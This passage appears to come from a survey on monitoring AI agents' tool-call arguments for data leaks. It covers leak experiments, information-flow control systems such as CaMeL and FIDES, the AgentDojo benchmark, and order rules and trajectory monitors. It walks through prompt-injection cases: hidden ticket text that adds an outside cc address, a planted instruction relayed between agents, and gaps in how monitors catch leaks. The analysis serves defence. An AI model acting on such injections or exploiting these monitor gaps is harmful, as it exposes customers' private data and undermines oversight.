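| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 4 | 2 | 2 | 3 |
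| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 0 | 2 | 2 | 1 |
| All models (of 30) | 20 (66.7%) | 18 (60.0%) | 14 (46.7%) | 8 (26.7%) |

Of the 120 sessions, 60 leaked an average of 3.25 of the four details each. The 20 leaks in the first column broke a rule that the models never saw, but 40 of the other 90 sessions leaked even though the rule they broke was in the prompt.

The overall fall from 66.7% with no visible rule to 26.7% with the strictest one comes entirely from the DeepSeek models, which went from 12 leaks in 12 sessions to none. The three Claude models together leaked in 8 of 18 sessions under both conditions, so the overall fall is not good evidence that stricter wording steadily helps. Haiku's low numbers also look slightly better than they should, because 10 of its 24 replies had no arguments that the software could read, and these counted as not leaking.

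So a company can't rely on a sentence in the prompt to keep data out of arguments, even if the sentence works perfectly with the model it uses today. The percentages themselves mean much less, because the experiment used one synthetic task and ran only one session per combination for each model. A single different outcome would move a cell by 17 percentage points. The output format also had a slot for each protected detail, and the experiment transmitted nothing.

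### The model's wording and the income test

Dong and colleagues also checked whether the text of a model's reply showed that it had leaked data. They searched for three kinds of wording: talk of authority and requirements, talk of a prohibition together with hesitation or necessity, and an explicit exception to the policy. The DeepSeek models leaked in 26 sessions without using either of the last two kinds. Haiku used the first kind most often and leaked least. A monitor that looked for a model explaining why it was breaking the rules would therefore have missed many leaks and flagged some harmless replies.

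An exact-copy search has its own limitation, because a model can use a protected detail without repeating it. If a customer's income led the model to offer a "luxury" product, the word would reveal something about the income. To test this, the researchers gave two DeepSeek models customer profiles that were identical except for income, which was $75,000, $175,000 or $275,000, and prohibited the models from using it. They ran each profile five times per model at each of two levels of pressure, for 60 calls in all.

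The researchers found no sign that income had influenced the arguments. The product tier, the field that should have shown an effect, was "standard" in all 60 calls. The arguments differed in 58 of 60 pairs of calls that differed only in income, but they also differed in all 120 pairs with the same income, because models rarely write the same free text twice.

A null result is informative only if the test could have found an effect, so the researchers also ran 30 calls in which the policy allowed income to set the tier. Both models matched tier to income every time, so the tier field can carry the information and the scoring can detect it. Anyone who looks for hidden influence in an agent's arguments needs the same two comparisons, one with the protected value unchanged and one with its use permitted. The null result covers only two models and one kind of data.

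### A monitor that ignores the model's reasons

Dong and colleagues designed a monitor that applies their test after the model proposes a call and before the tool runs. It relies only on information that the model can't change. Whoever registers a tool fixes its destination and the fields it may receive. The active task supplies the purpose, and each protected value carries a record of its source and permitted uses. The monitor ignores the model's explanations, retrieved documents, and claims of authority in the arguments, so a memo that calls a field mandatory doesn't affect the decision.

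For each call, the monitor rejects unknown tools and fields, then searches the remaining fields for canaries and exact copies of protected values. It also recognises the results of registered calculations. For example, if a registered calculation turns an income of $175,000 into a "premium" tier, the monitor can allow "premium" in a call about financing and block it in a call about marketing. It can't recognise paraphrases or the results of unregistered calculations. The design includes options to remove a value or ask a person, but the main configuration blocks the call.

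This design relies on a tool's registration to fix the destination, which works for a connection to one marketing service. An email tool like `send_email` fits awkwardly because the model writes the destination as an argument. The company would have to add something like a trusted staff directory so that the monitor could identify the address as the account manager's.

The researchers checked the monitor on calls based on 12 of their synthetic sessions. It blocked 12 calls that copied the profile. In a second set, about occupation, it blocked nine prohibited calls and passed three authorised ones, so all 24 decisions were correct. This shows that the program follows its own rules, but very little about how it would perform in use, because the researchers replayed prepared calls with complete records of where each value came from and haven't tested the monitor inside a running agent. Even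 if the three authorised calls had been a random sample, passing all three would be compatible with a false positive rate as high as 63% (at 95% confidence).

### Oversharing without an attacker

Agents also send too much data when nobody is trying to trick them. *AgentRaft* (Lin, Wu and colleagues, 2026) calls this data over-exposure. In its main example, a user asks an agent to send an auditor the date and amount of a payment. The tool that reads the file returns the whole transaction record, and the agent emails all of it, including the card number and security code. Tools that return whole records make this easy, because the extra data is already in the context when the agent writes its next call.

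Lin and colleagues define over-exposed data as data that the agent took from the source and sent to a third party, excluding what the user meant to send and what the task strictly needed. They count email recipients as third parties, so the account manager in the ticket 4417 case would be one.

The program AgentRaft looks for such cases before an agent goes into use. It first maps which tools can pass data to which others by comparing their input and output types and then asking a model whether each connection makes sense. For every route from a tool that reads private data to one that sends data out, it writes five realistic requests that specify which fields to share. It then runs the agent on these requests and traces the fields that reach the last tool. If a field wasn't in the request, three models vote on whether the task would have failed without it.

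To choose realistic tools, the researchers collected 6,675 tools from the directory MCP.so, then built four test agents with a total of 233 functions. AgentRaft reported over-exposure on 319 of the 474 routes it tested, and human reviewers confirmed 295 of these (92.5%). The researchers could not say what share of all over-exposure AgentRaft found, because nobody has a complete list of cases.

They also tested five existing agents: Claude Code, Codex, Gemini CLI, OpenClaw and Hermes. Over-exposure occurred at least once on 759 of 2,337 routes (32.5%) and in 26.3% of individual runs. In those runs, about 80% of the fields the agents sent were surplus. All five agents used the same DeepSeek model instead of their usual ones, so the figures isolate the effect of the software around the model but don't describe the products as sold. The effect was large, with Claude Code over-exposing data in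 11.7% of runs and Codex in 33.6%.

Newer models still overshare. *AgentCIScope* (Guo, Chen and colleagues, 2026) tested 12 combinations of model and agent software on 936 office tasks involving email, calendars and similar tools. The share of tasks in which private data reached someone who shouldn't have it ranged from 32.5% (Claude Opus 5 in Claude Code) to 94.4% (Gemini 3.8 Flash in Google's agent kit). These rates are high partly because the researchers kept only tasks on which another agent had already leaked data.

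The differences between types of data probably matter more. On average, agents leaked credit card information 17.1% of the time, booking details 76.5%, and personal preferences 84.7%. Content scanning is weakest on the data these agents overshared most, because preferences have no fixed format, while card numbers are the easiest data for a scanner to find.

### Writing the rules down

Dong and colleagues' monitor needs a written policy. Privacy law provides some evidence that such policies are possible. Nissenbaum reports an analysis that found all five parameters in US health and financial privacy rules. One health rule, for example, lets a provider show psychotherapy notes to the patient only with the psychiatrist's approval. *Privacy Conductor* (2026) describes how Barth and colleagues expressed norms from legislation in a formal logic that a computer can check. Their system took the norms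 as input, so somebody still had to supply them. Later researchers have used surveys to find out what people consider appropriate.

Rules are easiest to manage in a closed setting. Nissenbaum notes that a hospital has limited roles and types of information, so there are fewer combinations to consider. *The Stochastic Deputy* (2026) describes a similar approach for hotels. The software masks guests' contact details and dates of birth in every tool result before the agent reads it, but keeps their names, because a front-desk manager who asks who is arriving today needs them. It decides what to mask by column name, so it also masks a harmless switchboard number in a column called `phone`. The designers accept such mistakes because they consider masking too much safer than masking too little. They also provided no way to turn the masking off, because they expect that somebody would eventually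 do so and that this would be discovered during an incident investigation.

Field rules have advantages over a model's judgement. They give the same result every time, an auditor can read them, a persuasive memo can't change them, and they are fast. In *ToolMinimize*, Li and Xu (2026) built a program that rewrites arguments to contain only what the tool needs. For instance, it replaces the name of a cancer hospital in a weather lookup with the city. Its rule-based version typically took under two milliseconds per call.

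But the same program shows two ways that field rules fail. Its rules treated the body of an email as necessary, so they left everything in it, including irrelevant mentions of a lost job. To remove those, Li and Xu had to ask a second model about each item, which took about 800 milliseconds per call. The rules also removed too much. When the researchers ran 20 rewritten tasks against simulated services, four failed because the program had deleted addresses that a map tool needed.

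Free-text fields, such as an email body, are common. *ArguShield* (Fu and Fu, 2026) cites an analysis of 2,344 tool specifications for OpenAI's custom GPTs, in which 36.9% had at least one loosely constrained text field, such as `notes` or `context`. The monitor has to find the values inside this text before it can apply a rule to them.

*Say Something Else* (2026) argues that fixed filters alone can't protect privacy, and neither can asking users to list every sensitive detail in advance, because the same detail may be fine to tell a close friend and risky to tell a manager. This is a good argument against rules based only on the type of data. It is weaker against rules that also specify the recipient and purpose, although the number of combinations then grows quickly.

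### Who decides what a task needs

In these studies, the researchers, their annotators or a panel of models decided what a task needed. A human annotator reviewed 157 items that AgentCIScope treats as private and agreed on 94.3% of them. But Guo and colleagues had already removed any item on which three simulated people, with strict, moderate and relaxed attitudes to privacy, disagreed, so the figure describes agreement on clear cases.

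The remaining disagreements were reasonable. The annotator thought that hotel staff could use some of a guest's preferences to give better service, and that a scholarship committee might need detailed academic records. *CI-Work* (2026), a benchmark for workplace agents, has an "Ambiguous" label for items that are neither clearly essential nor clearly sensitive.

A company's customer support manager could probably decide which details belong in a ticket summary, with advice from whoever handles data protection. The employee who makes the request is a less suitable judge, because they can explain the task but can't consent on the customer's behalf to a disclosure that the company prohibits.

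### Vague requests

AgentRaft avoids the problem of vague requests because each of its test requests specifies the fields to share. Real users often leave the fields unspecified. If the employee had asked the agent to send the account manager "whatever they need to sort this out", whether the home address was necessary would have depended on how the account manager planned to sort it out.

Fu and Fu's ArguShield labels each value "keep", "ask" or "hide" according to where it came from, whether the task needs it and whether the recipient may have it. If the evidence is unclear, it asks the user rather than sending the value silently. On standard tasks with four models, it reduced the average rate of unauthorised silent release from 84% to 9%. A privacy instruction in the prompt reduced it at least as much, but the agents then completed only 55% to 87% of the tasks. With ArguShield they completed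 97% if the user approved every request, and 93% if the user refused them all.

Those users were simulated, and real ones might tire of the questions, since ArguShield asked about roughly one value in five. Most of its remaining mistakes were overcautious: 43% withheld too much and 39% were unnecessary questions. The other 18% released data that should have been withheld. The final decision follows a fixed rule, but the program first has to estimate what the task needs. Fu and Fu acknowledge that an ambiguous request can still lead to a wrong release.

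One of Guo and colleagues' test cases suggests a way to make decisions depend less on the request. A recruiter asked an agent running GPT-6 Astra to email an engineering manager about where each job candidate stood. The recruiter asked it to be complete and to quote its sources on anything that affected a candidate's standing. The agent included a background-check note about a minor criminal offence in 2017, which Guo and colleagues count as a leak. But the compliance team's review of the offence was still pending, so a conscientious human assistant could have thought the request covered the note.

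A monitor that tried to work out what the email needed could easily have made the same mistake. A rule that engineering managers may not receive background checks would have ruled out sending one, whatever the recruiter wrote. It therefore makes sense to start by writing down who may never receive which data, since those restrictions usually depend on roles and change slowly. The data a task needs changes with every request and is much harder to specify in advance.

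For ticket 4417, the company could ban full card numbers from every email the agent sends, because hardly any support task needs one. It could also let the agent send home addresses to account managers but not to outside archives. These rules wouldn't remove an unnecessary address from the summary, but including one would be a much smaller mistake than sending the card number.

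## Tracking where each argument value came from

The checks described so far examine an argument's value but not where it came from. If the employee supplied the outside address in the copy field of the ticket 4417 email, it may belong to a supplier that archives the company's email. But if the address came from a complaint that a stranger typed into a web form, it shouldn't determine where the company sends a customer's data.

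Information-flow control is an established security method for tracking where data came from. Software labels data when it enters a system, carries the labels along as programs combine and transform the data, and checks them before any data leaves. With agents, this method has stopped nearly all the prompt injections in a standard benchmark, but the protected agents complete far fewer tasks.

### Labels and the rule at the call

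A label records who may read a value (its confidentiality) and whether an untrusted person could have influenced it (its integrity). *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses a scheme that goes back to a 1976 paper by the computer scientist Dorothy Denning. When software combines two values, the result's label allows only people who may read both values to read the result, and marks it as trusted only if both values are trusted.

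Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives the example of an agent that answers Alex's email. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet, has also emailed Alex. Once the agent has read both emails, the permitted readers of its reply are {Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}, so it can't send the reply to Marco without asking.

For an email tool, a strict version of the rules looks like this:

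```text
readers(a combined with b) = readers(a) ∩ readers(b)
trusted(a combined with b) = trusted(a) and trusted(b)

send_email(recipients, body) may run only if
    every recipient is in readers(body), and
    the recipients are trusted values, and
    the decision to send came from trusted data
```

Suppose the outside address in the ticket 4417 email came from hidden text in the complaint. Anyone can write a ticket, so the lookup tool labels the complaint untrusted when it returns the record. The address keeps that label when it reaches the `cc` field, so the software refuses the call. The account manager's address would pass because it came from the employee's request, which is trusted. The card number fails the readers test if only the employee and the billing team may see it.

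The same rule would catch an overzealous agent that copied the email to a contractor named in the ticket, because the contractor's address also came from untrusted text. If the employee had asked the agent to send a copy to their own private mailbox, the address would count as trusted, and only the readers test could stop the email.

### Why a language model taints everything

In an ordinary program, software can follow a value from one variable to the next, but a language model can use any part of its context when it writes any word. The `to`, `cc` and `body` values all come from one response, which doesn't show what each depended on. An exact-copy search, like the one in Dong and colleagues' monitor, misses reworded values.

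The safe assumption is that every argument depends on everything in the context. But once the agent has read the complaint, this makes even the account manager's address untrusted (or "tainted"), so the software refuses the legitimate email as well as the one that leaks data. The assumption also shrinks the set of permitted readers. A summary written after the model has read the whole ticket inherits the restrictions on the card number, even if it doesn't contain the number. Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) study this problem, known as label creep, in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*.

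Some researchers try to work out which inputs actually influenced an argument's value. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) describes NeuroTaint, which uses the record of a run to trace the influence of each source. In 400 test scenarios, it found 93.5% of the real flows from a source to a sensitive call, and 92.1% of the flows it reported were real. It works only after the run, so it can help explain a leak but can't prevent one.

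### CaMeL

The two best-known designs keep untrusted text away from the model that chooses the tool calls. Both build on the Dual LLM pattern, which Willison proposed in April 2023. In this pattern, a privileged model plans the work and can use tools but never reads untrusted text, which is read instead by a quarantined model that has no tools.

Google DeepMind researchers presented CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). According to Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, it works as follows:

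1. The privileged model reads the user's request and writes a program for the whole task in a restricted version of Python.
2. CaMeL's interpreter runs the program and calls the tools. It labels each result with its sources and permitted readers.
3. When the program needs something from untrusted text, the quarantined model extracts it in a fixed format, such as an email address. The extracted value inherits the text's labels.
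4. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, which is a short function that examines the arguments and their labels and either allows or denies the call.

For ticket 4417, the program might look like this:

```python
ticket = get_ticket(4417)
summary = ask_quarantined_model("Summarise this", ticket.complaint)
send_email(to="account.manager@company.example", body=summary)
```

The privileged model writes this program before anything opens the ticket, so hidden text in the complaint can't add a copy field. The program passes on only the complaint, so the summary doesn't inherit the restrictions on the card number stored elsewhere in the record.

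The labels are essential when an argument has to come from untrusted text. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, discusses a user who asks an agent to send a document to Bob, whose address is in meeting notes. An attacker who can add text to the notes can make the quarantined model return a different address, and the agent will then follow its plan and send the document there. Willison's original pattern had no defence against this. CaMeL can trace the address to the notes, and its policy can refuse an unknown address or ask the user.

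### FIDES

FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, lets the model choose each step as it goes. It labels every field of a tool result. If a field is less trusted than the conversation so far, FIDES stores it in memory and shows the model only a variable name. The model can use that name as an argument, and FIDES inserts the real value, with its label, just before the call.

With ticket 4417, the model would receive a variable name in place of the complaint. It would call a quarantined model to summarise the variable's contents, get back the name of a second variable, and use that variable as the body of the email. Because the model hasn't received the complaint's text, the conversation is still trusted, and so is the account manager's address.

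Sometimes the model needs a variable's contents to choose the next step. It can reveal them, but this makes the conversation untrusted, and the policy may block later calls. The design also lets the quarantined model give a restricted answer, such as yes or no. A yes-or-no answer gives an attacker at most one bit of influence, so a policy may allow actions based on it. The tests described below didn't use this option.

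CaMeL is stricter because its privileged model has to write the whole program in advance. FIDES can handle tasks whose next step depends on what the agent finds, but it may then block the agent from acting.

### Results on AgentDojo

Researchers have mostly tested these systems on *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark with 97 realistic tasks and, in its first version, 629 security test cases. The tasks cover office work, banking, travel and Slack messaging. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) explains that the attacks appear where text from outsiders normally would, such as in an email body. Fixed code then checks the outcome, such as whether an email was sent, without using a model as a judge.

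With GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary agent. Hiding untrusted values reduced this to 21, and adding the policy checks reduced it to none. AgentDojo still counted three successes, but Costa and colleagues examined them and concluded that they weren't real injections.

The table gives the percentage of tasks completed when there was no attack. The "labels only" agent has policy checks but doesn't hide anything from the model.

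| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack | Mean |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, GPT-4o | 75 | 70 | 99 | 93 | 84 |
| Labels only, GPT-4o | 37 | 73 | 38 | 20 | 42 |
| FIDES with checks, GPT-4o | 59 | 41 | 53 | 48 | 50 |
| Ordinary agent, o1 | 70 | 82 | 96 | 88 | 84 |
| FIDES with checks, o1 | 65 | 68 | 56 | 54 | 61 |

The "labels only" row shows how much work tainting can block. Hiding values recovers some of that work, and using OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, recovers more. Even then, FIDES completed about 23 percentage points fewer tasks than an ordinary agent with the same model.

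*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) summarises CaMeL's original results as nearly complete protection with comparable task performance. Later tests by other researchers confirmed the protection but found a much larger loss in task performance. In *SecureClaw* (2026), none of 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks run without an attack. In *Kairos* (2026), which used GPT-4.1 and turned on CaMeL's policies, 0.4% of attacks succeeded and CaMeL completed 40% of tasks. Nikolaou and colleagues used Claude Haiku 4.5 and got a completion rate of 51%.

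Part of this loss in task completion should shrink as models improve, because better models are better at writing programs for data they can't see. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested CaMeL without security policies on a set of industrial tasks. CaMeL reduced task completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by only 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Fable 5.

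The policies also reduce how many tasks the agent completes, and a better model may not help much with this. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) reports that CaMeL's completion rate on one set of 16 tasks fell to 37.5% with its policies on, for both models tested. Some of these tasks require the agent to read an untrusted file and then act on it, which the policy prohibits. *SPA* (2026) found a similar drop in a different system, from 53% to 29%, with flow control on.

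### How much the tests prove

Costa and colleagues marked a field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack used it. This gave them a clear baseline, but a company can't know in advance which fields attackers will use. It would have to either mark more data as untrusted, in which case its agent would probably complete fewer tasks, or leave some vulnerable fields marked as trusted.

The policies used to test FIDES also ignored the labels on individual arguments when deciding whether to trust a call. If the employee had asked the agent to email the summary to "the contact named in the ticket", these policies could have let the agent send it to an attacker's address, because the decision to send came from the employee. FIDES can also require a trusted recipient, and that stricter setting seems essential for monitoring arguments.

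AgentDojo is also becoming less useful for testing attacks. In Peters-Gill and colleagues' experiments, none of its attacks worked on undefended GPT-5.5, and 1.5% worked on undefended Fable 5. *APPA* (2026) left the benchmark out for this reason. Peters-Gill and colleagues point out that these low success rates don't make the models safe against attackers who adapt. Fable 5 also refused 52 of the 97 harmless tasks, possibly because it associated the benchmark with attacks.

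### Attacks outside the guarantee

CaMeL and FIDES assume that the user, the tools and the tool descriptions are trustworthy, so a poisoned tool description can still redirect the agent. They also don't protect against the model's own mistakes. The agent that deleted a whole drive was acting on a trusted request, so checking only where its arguments came from would have allowed the deletion.

An attacker can still corrupt the text the agent passes on. Hidden instructions in the complaint could make the quarantined model write a false or empty summary, and the account manager would receive it. Neither system fully prevents leaks through the agent's choices. FIDES controls direct flows of data, but an observer might learn something from which tools the agent calls and in what order, as the website's owner did in the `web_fetch` case. In CaMeL, untrusted data can determine which branch of the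 program runs, though it can't add a new branch.

The protection can also fail when one agent gives work to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three agents, each running CaMeL without security policies, and asked them to send a colleague a Slack message summarizing job applicants. An instruction planted in the database passed through the first two agents as data. The coordinating agent then included it in its written request to the messaging agent. The messaging agent treated the whole request as coming from its user and emailed the applicants' details to an outside address.

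The paper's fix, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data between agents separately and keeps the labels attached. It stopped all the attacks in the paper's multi-agent version of AgentDojo. On the industrial tasks, it lowered performance by 3.2 percentage points more than running CaMeL in each agent did.

### Successors in 2026

Several newer systems try to reduce this burden. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) introduces Prudentia, an extension of FIDES that shows the model the labels and policies so that it can plan around them. Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse, or vouch for, a piece of data. If an email lists ten jobs, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten calls.

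Kolluri and colleagues also argue that the usual comparison is unfair because it compares an agent that never asks for help with an unprotected one that may do anything, while many real products ask for approval before consequential actions. They therefore counted the tasks that each agent completed without any approval. With OpenAI's o3-mini, an ordinary agent that had to ask before every consequential call completed 24.3%, FIDES 50.1% and Prudentia 59.1%. Labels could mean fewer interruptions for a company that already requires approvals. This count assumes that people always make the right decision, which makes every system in the comparison look better than it is.

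APPA helps an agent recover after the policy blocks a call. On its developers' own set of 200 office tasks, it completed 88% to 90% with each of three models, and none of 600 attacks succeeded. Versions without enforcement completed 90% to 92.5% of the tasks, but 30% to 39.5% of the attacks succeeded. Enforcement reduced task completion much less here than on AgentDojo, although a benchmark by a system's own developers is weaker evidence than an independent one.

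Nikolaou and colleagues' CaMeLoT checks CaMeL's program before it runs, and can also enforce rules about the order of calls.

### Use in products

Microsoft has added FIDES to Agent Framework, its toolkit for building agents. *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (May 2026) calls the feature experimental. In its example, an agent reads a public bug report with a hidden instruction to post the contents of a secret file in a public comment. The agent is allowed to open the file, but the software then treats the conversation as private and blocks the comment or asks a person to approve it.

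Labels are only useful across tools from different suppliers if the tools can exchange them. Microsoft and GitHub have built a version of GitHub's MCP server that attaches labels to its results, and an experimental mode of GitHub's command-line agent that checks them. Microsoft says it will work with the MCP community on adding labels to the standard. These labels would have stopped the GitHub leak in Willison's account of the lethal trifecta, because the agent could not have posted publicly after reading both an untrusted public issue and private code.

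GitHub uses a simpler form of this tracking in Agentic Workflows, its system for running agents on code projects. A gateway removes content written by insufficiently trusted people before the model reads it, and GitHub logs each removal. According to GitHub's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering*, trust depends on an author's relationship to the project and on whether a maintainer has approved the content, which they can do with a thumbs-up. The system also tracks private data but doesn't yet stop it from leaving, so it controls what the agent reads more than what it sends.

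None of these announcements reports how often the labels stopped a leak or held up legitimate work. Flow control for agents has moved from research into real software, but there is still little evidence of how well it works in everyday use.

### The case for origin

The best argument for tracking origin is that attackers can change an input's wording more easily than its origin. If the software labels every ticket from the public as untrusted, rewriting a ticket to be more persuasive doesn't change its label. Microsoft stresses that a check on origin doesn't depend on the model's judgement, so the model doesn't have to notice the attack. By contrast, GitHub describes content filtering as a cat-and-mouse game.

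Checking a value's origin also gives a definite answer when its content is ambiguous, as with the outside address. A judgement about the agent's intent would depend on text the attacker may have written. These are strong reasons to prefer origin for deciding who may influence a consequential call. The other checks are still needed, because a trusted employee can make a harmful request and a trusted database can contain a card number that the agent shouldn't send out.

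### Labels, approvals and open-ended work

The guarantee depends on someone supplying correct labels. Microsoft's toolkit treats a tool without a label as trusted and public, so a developer who forgot to label the ticket lookup would lose the protection without any warning. A broad label can also be wrong for some of the data it covers. GitHub's MCP server labels everything in a private repository as trusted. Many companies automatically copy customers' complaints into Jira. If a company copied them into a private GitHub repository instead, text written by outsiders would be labeled as trusted.

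Lists of permitted readers are also hard to keep accurate. Costa and colleagues treated an email's sender and recipients as its readers, but acknowledge that someone may have shared it more widely. Willison welcomed CaMeL as the first defence against prompt injection to offer strong guarantees, but was "deeply nervous" about requiring users to think about security policies.

Exceptions are unavoidable because labels only get stricter as data accumulates. Gregory and colleagues simulated thousands of tasks spread over teams of agents and found that more direct connections between agents, or giving the sensitive tools to only a few of them, slowed this label creep, but no arrangement they tested prevented it. Someone therefore has to decide when to relax a label, which can add to the approval requests that users tire of. Endorsing a whole email is quicker than approving ten calls, but a user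 who overlooks a hidden instruction in the email endorses that instruction too.

Open-ended tasks are the hardest for this approach to handle. Costa and colleagues classed over 40% of AgentDojo's banking and Slack tasks as ones where the next step depends on what the agent reads, compared with 5% of its office tasks. *AgentDyn* (2026), a benchmark with more changeable tasks, found that several kinds of protected agent did much worse on it than on AgentDojo, so AgentDojo results may understate how much defences in general reduce performance.

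Better engineering can't entirely solve this, because a legitimate address can have the same origin as one planted by an attacker. For example, a customer might write "please send the refund letter to my accountant" and give an address. A rule that recipients must come from a trusted source would block both addresses. The company could compare the address with the contacts in the customer's record, or have an employee confirm it. Neither check would be necessary for ticket 4417, because the employee had already said who should receive the summary.

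## Judging a series of calls together

A monitor can detect some harm only by looking at several calls together. The support agent is allowed to look up any customer, so a check on a single lookup would find nothing wrong. But if the agent looks up 4,000 customers in one night, somebody may be copying the customer database. To notice this, the monitor needs a record of what the agent did earlier. Longer records reveal more but take more time and money to read, and a verdict on a finished run comes too late to stop the calls in it. The most promising approach is to read the earlier calls and decide on each new one before it runs.

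### One call, one session or many agents

The order of calls can matter as much as their number. Suppose a private note on ticket 4417 says the company would pay up to $400 to settle the complaint. The agent reads the note, then emails the customer to ask whether $400 would be acceptable. The email goes to the right person, makes a polite offer and contains no personal data. Only someone who knows the agent had just read the note can tell that the email reveals the company's limit.

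A monitor can examine one call, one session (a single run of the agent), or many sessions and agents together. A trajectory is the ordered record of a session, including its requests, calls, results and replies.

| What the monitor reads | Example of what it can notice | What it needs |
|---|---|---|
| One call | A card number in an email | The call's arguments |
| One session | An offer that repeats a figure from a private note | The ordered record of the run, including tool results |
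| Many sessions and agents | Forty agents that each copy a small part of the database | A shared store of records, with matching times and identities |

How much of a session a monitor reads is a separate choice from which calls it judges. It can read the whole session and judge only the next call. Operators usually want this because the next call is the only one the monitor can still stop.

In the July 2026 `web_fetch` gap, every link was permitted and only the sequence of links revealed the user's details. A task split between tools is similarly hard to judge from a single call, as when one call writes a draft and another sends it by its identifier. A monitor that keeps the session's record can use the identifier to look up the draft. But that record also contains the card number and everything else the agent read, so the company has to protect it as carefully as the ticket system.

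### Rules about order

The simplest way to use a session's record is to write rules about which calls may follow which. An early language for such rules came with Invariant Labs' *Invariant Security Analyzer*, an open-source program from 2024. One of its published examples refuses an email to anyone outside the organisation once the agent has read the inbox. Adapted to the support agent and slightly simplified, the rule looks like this:

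```text
raise "no outside email after reading a ticket" if:
    (earlier: ToolCall) -> (later: ToolCall)
    earlier is tool:get_ticket
    later is tool:send_email({ to: <address outside company.example> })
```

The arrow means that data from the earlier call can flow into the later one. A language model can use anything in its context, so in practice this probably covers any later email in the same session. When the agent proposes an email to an outsider, the monitor checks for an earlier ticket lookup. If it finds one, it reports a violation, and the agent's software can refuse the call. The monitor can check the record before and after every tool use, or analyse a finished run.

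This rule is a cruder version of the labels in information-flow control. Like a destination check, it still works if the agent rewords or encodes the data. It would have stopped the $400 offer without anyone labelling the private note. But it would also stop all other emails to customers about their tickets, which are most of what a support agent writes.

Invariant Labs has a narrower example, in which an agent that has opened an email may write only to that email's sender. The monitor gets the sender's address from the earlier result and compares it with the new argument. A similar rule for tickets could permit emails only to the customer and the account manager, which would block the email to the outside archive but allow the $400 offer. Invariant Labs' later documentation describes a variant that blocks an email only if the inbox contained a suspected prompt injection. That would interrupt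 less work, but it depends on a detector recognising the injection.

The published inbox rule also has gaps common in simple allowlists. It checks `to` but not `cc`, and it treats any domain that begins with the company's name as internal.

A rule also can't use information that is missing from its record. If one agent reads the ticket and passes a summary to a second agent, which then sends the email, the second agent's session contains no ticket lookup. The monitor would need to link the two sessions to connect the email to the lookup.

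### Volume limits and baselines

A volume limit needs a running count, a time window, and a decision about whose calls to count together. An example in the documentation of Nylas, which provides email accounts for agents, refuses to send a message if the account has already sent 50 in the past hour. The example keeps the count in the program's memory, so restarting the program resets it to zero, and two copies of the program could send 50 messages each. Nylas also has a daily limit on the account, which is harder to get around by accident.

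Counting calls can understate how many people they affect. An email to 200 people is one call, and so is a database query that returns 4,000 customers. The monitor has to read the email call's arguments to count the recipients and the query's results to count the customers.

A fixed limit works well if the operator knows the most the agent could legitimately need. Otherwise the monitor can compare the count with a baseline, a record of normal behaviour. This requires enough history from a period without a leak, and separate baselines for agents that do different jobs. The operator also has to update each baseline when the work changes, or the monitor will flag the new work as suspicious.

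Baselines can reveal activity that somebody has spread over many agents. Suppose 40 support agents each make an average of 100 lookups a night, with a standard deviation (a measure of the usual variation) of 20. Someone gets each agent to make 30 extra lookups, which together cover 1,200 customers. The calculation below shows how unusual this is for one agent and for all 40 together, assuming their workloads vary independently.

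```text
One agent:   30 / 20              = 1.5 standard deviations above average
All 40:      1,200 / (20 × √40)   ≈ 9.5 standard deviations above average
```

If the counts follow a normal distribution, about 7% of an agent's ordinary nights are at least as busy as this. A monitor that flagged every such night would raise two or three false alarms a night across the 40 agents. But the agents' combined total would almost never be this high by chance, because the extra lookups add up while random variations partly cancel out.

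Real workloads aren't independent, since a faulty product can increase every agent's tickets at once. Counting lookups per ticket would help. But a count can only show that something unusual is happening, and it can't catch the $400 offer, which was a single email.

### Models that read whole runs

Rules and counts cover only the patterns somebody thought of in advance. A model can read a run and look for problems more generally, but tests suggest that it makes many mistakes. *ATBench* (Li, Luo and colleagues, 2026) tested models on 1,000 synthetic runs, 503 safe and 497 unsafe. The runs average nine turns and about 4,000 tokens (the word fragments that models process).

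For each run, a planning program chose a risk, a set of tools and a point where the risk would appear. Models then simulated the request, the tool calls, the results and the agent's replies. Li and colleagues made safe and unsafe versions of the same scenario, so that a model couldn't score well just by recognising a risky topic. In some runs, a risk introduced early takes effect only several turns later. Human reviewers audited every run and changed five of the safe/unsafe labels.

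The table gives results for some of the tested models. The miss rate is the share of unsafe runs that a model judged safe. The false positive rate, calculated here from the published scores, is the share of safe runs that a model judged unsafe.

| Model | Type | Miss rate | False positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.4 | General-purpose | 13% | 40% |
| Gemini 3 Flash | General-purpose | 29% | 18% |
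| AgentDoG | Guard for agents | 11% | 61% |
| Llama Guard 4 | Guard for chat | 69% | about 17% |
| Llama Guard 3 | Guard for chat | 96% | about 1% |
| Qwen3-Guard | Guard for chat | over 99% | about 1% |

Developers train guard models specifically to detect unsafe content or behaviour. Llama Guard 3 and Qwen3-Guard had low false positive rates because they classified almost everything as safe. They check for harmful text, but an unsafe run may contain only polite text and ordinary tool calls. AgentDoG had an advantage because ATBench is part of the same project, according to *Benchmarks for Trajectory Safety Evaluation and Diagnosis in OpenClaw and Codex* (2026).

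The models were much worse at explaining what had gone wrong. GPT-5.4 identified the source of the risk in 33.6% of unsafe runs and the type of failure in 13.5%. A reviewer who received its alerts would often have to work out the cause themselves.

These false positive rates would probably be lower in ordinary work, where few safe runs are near-copies of unsafe ones. Newer models would probably do better too.

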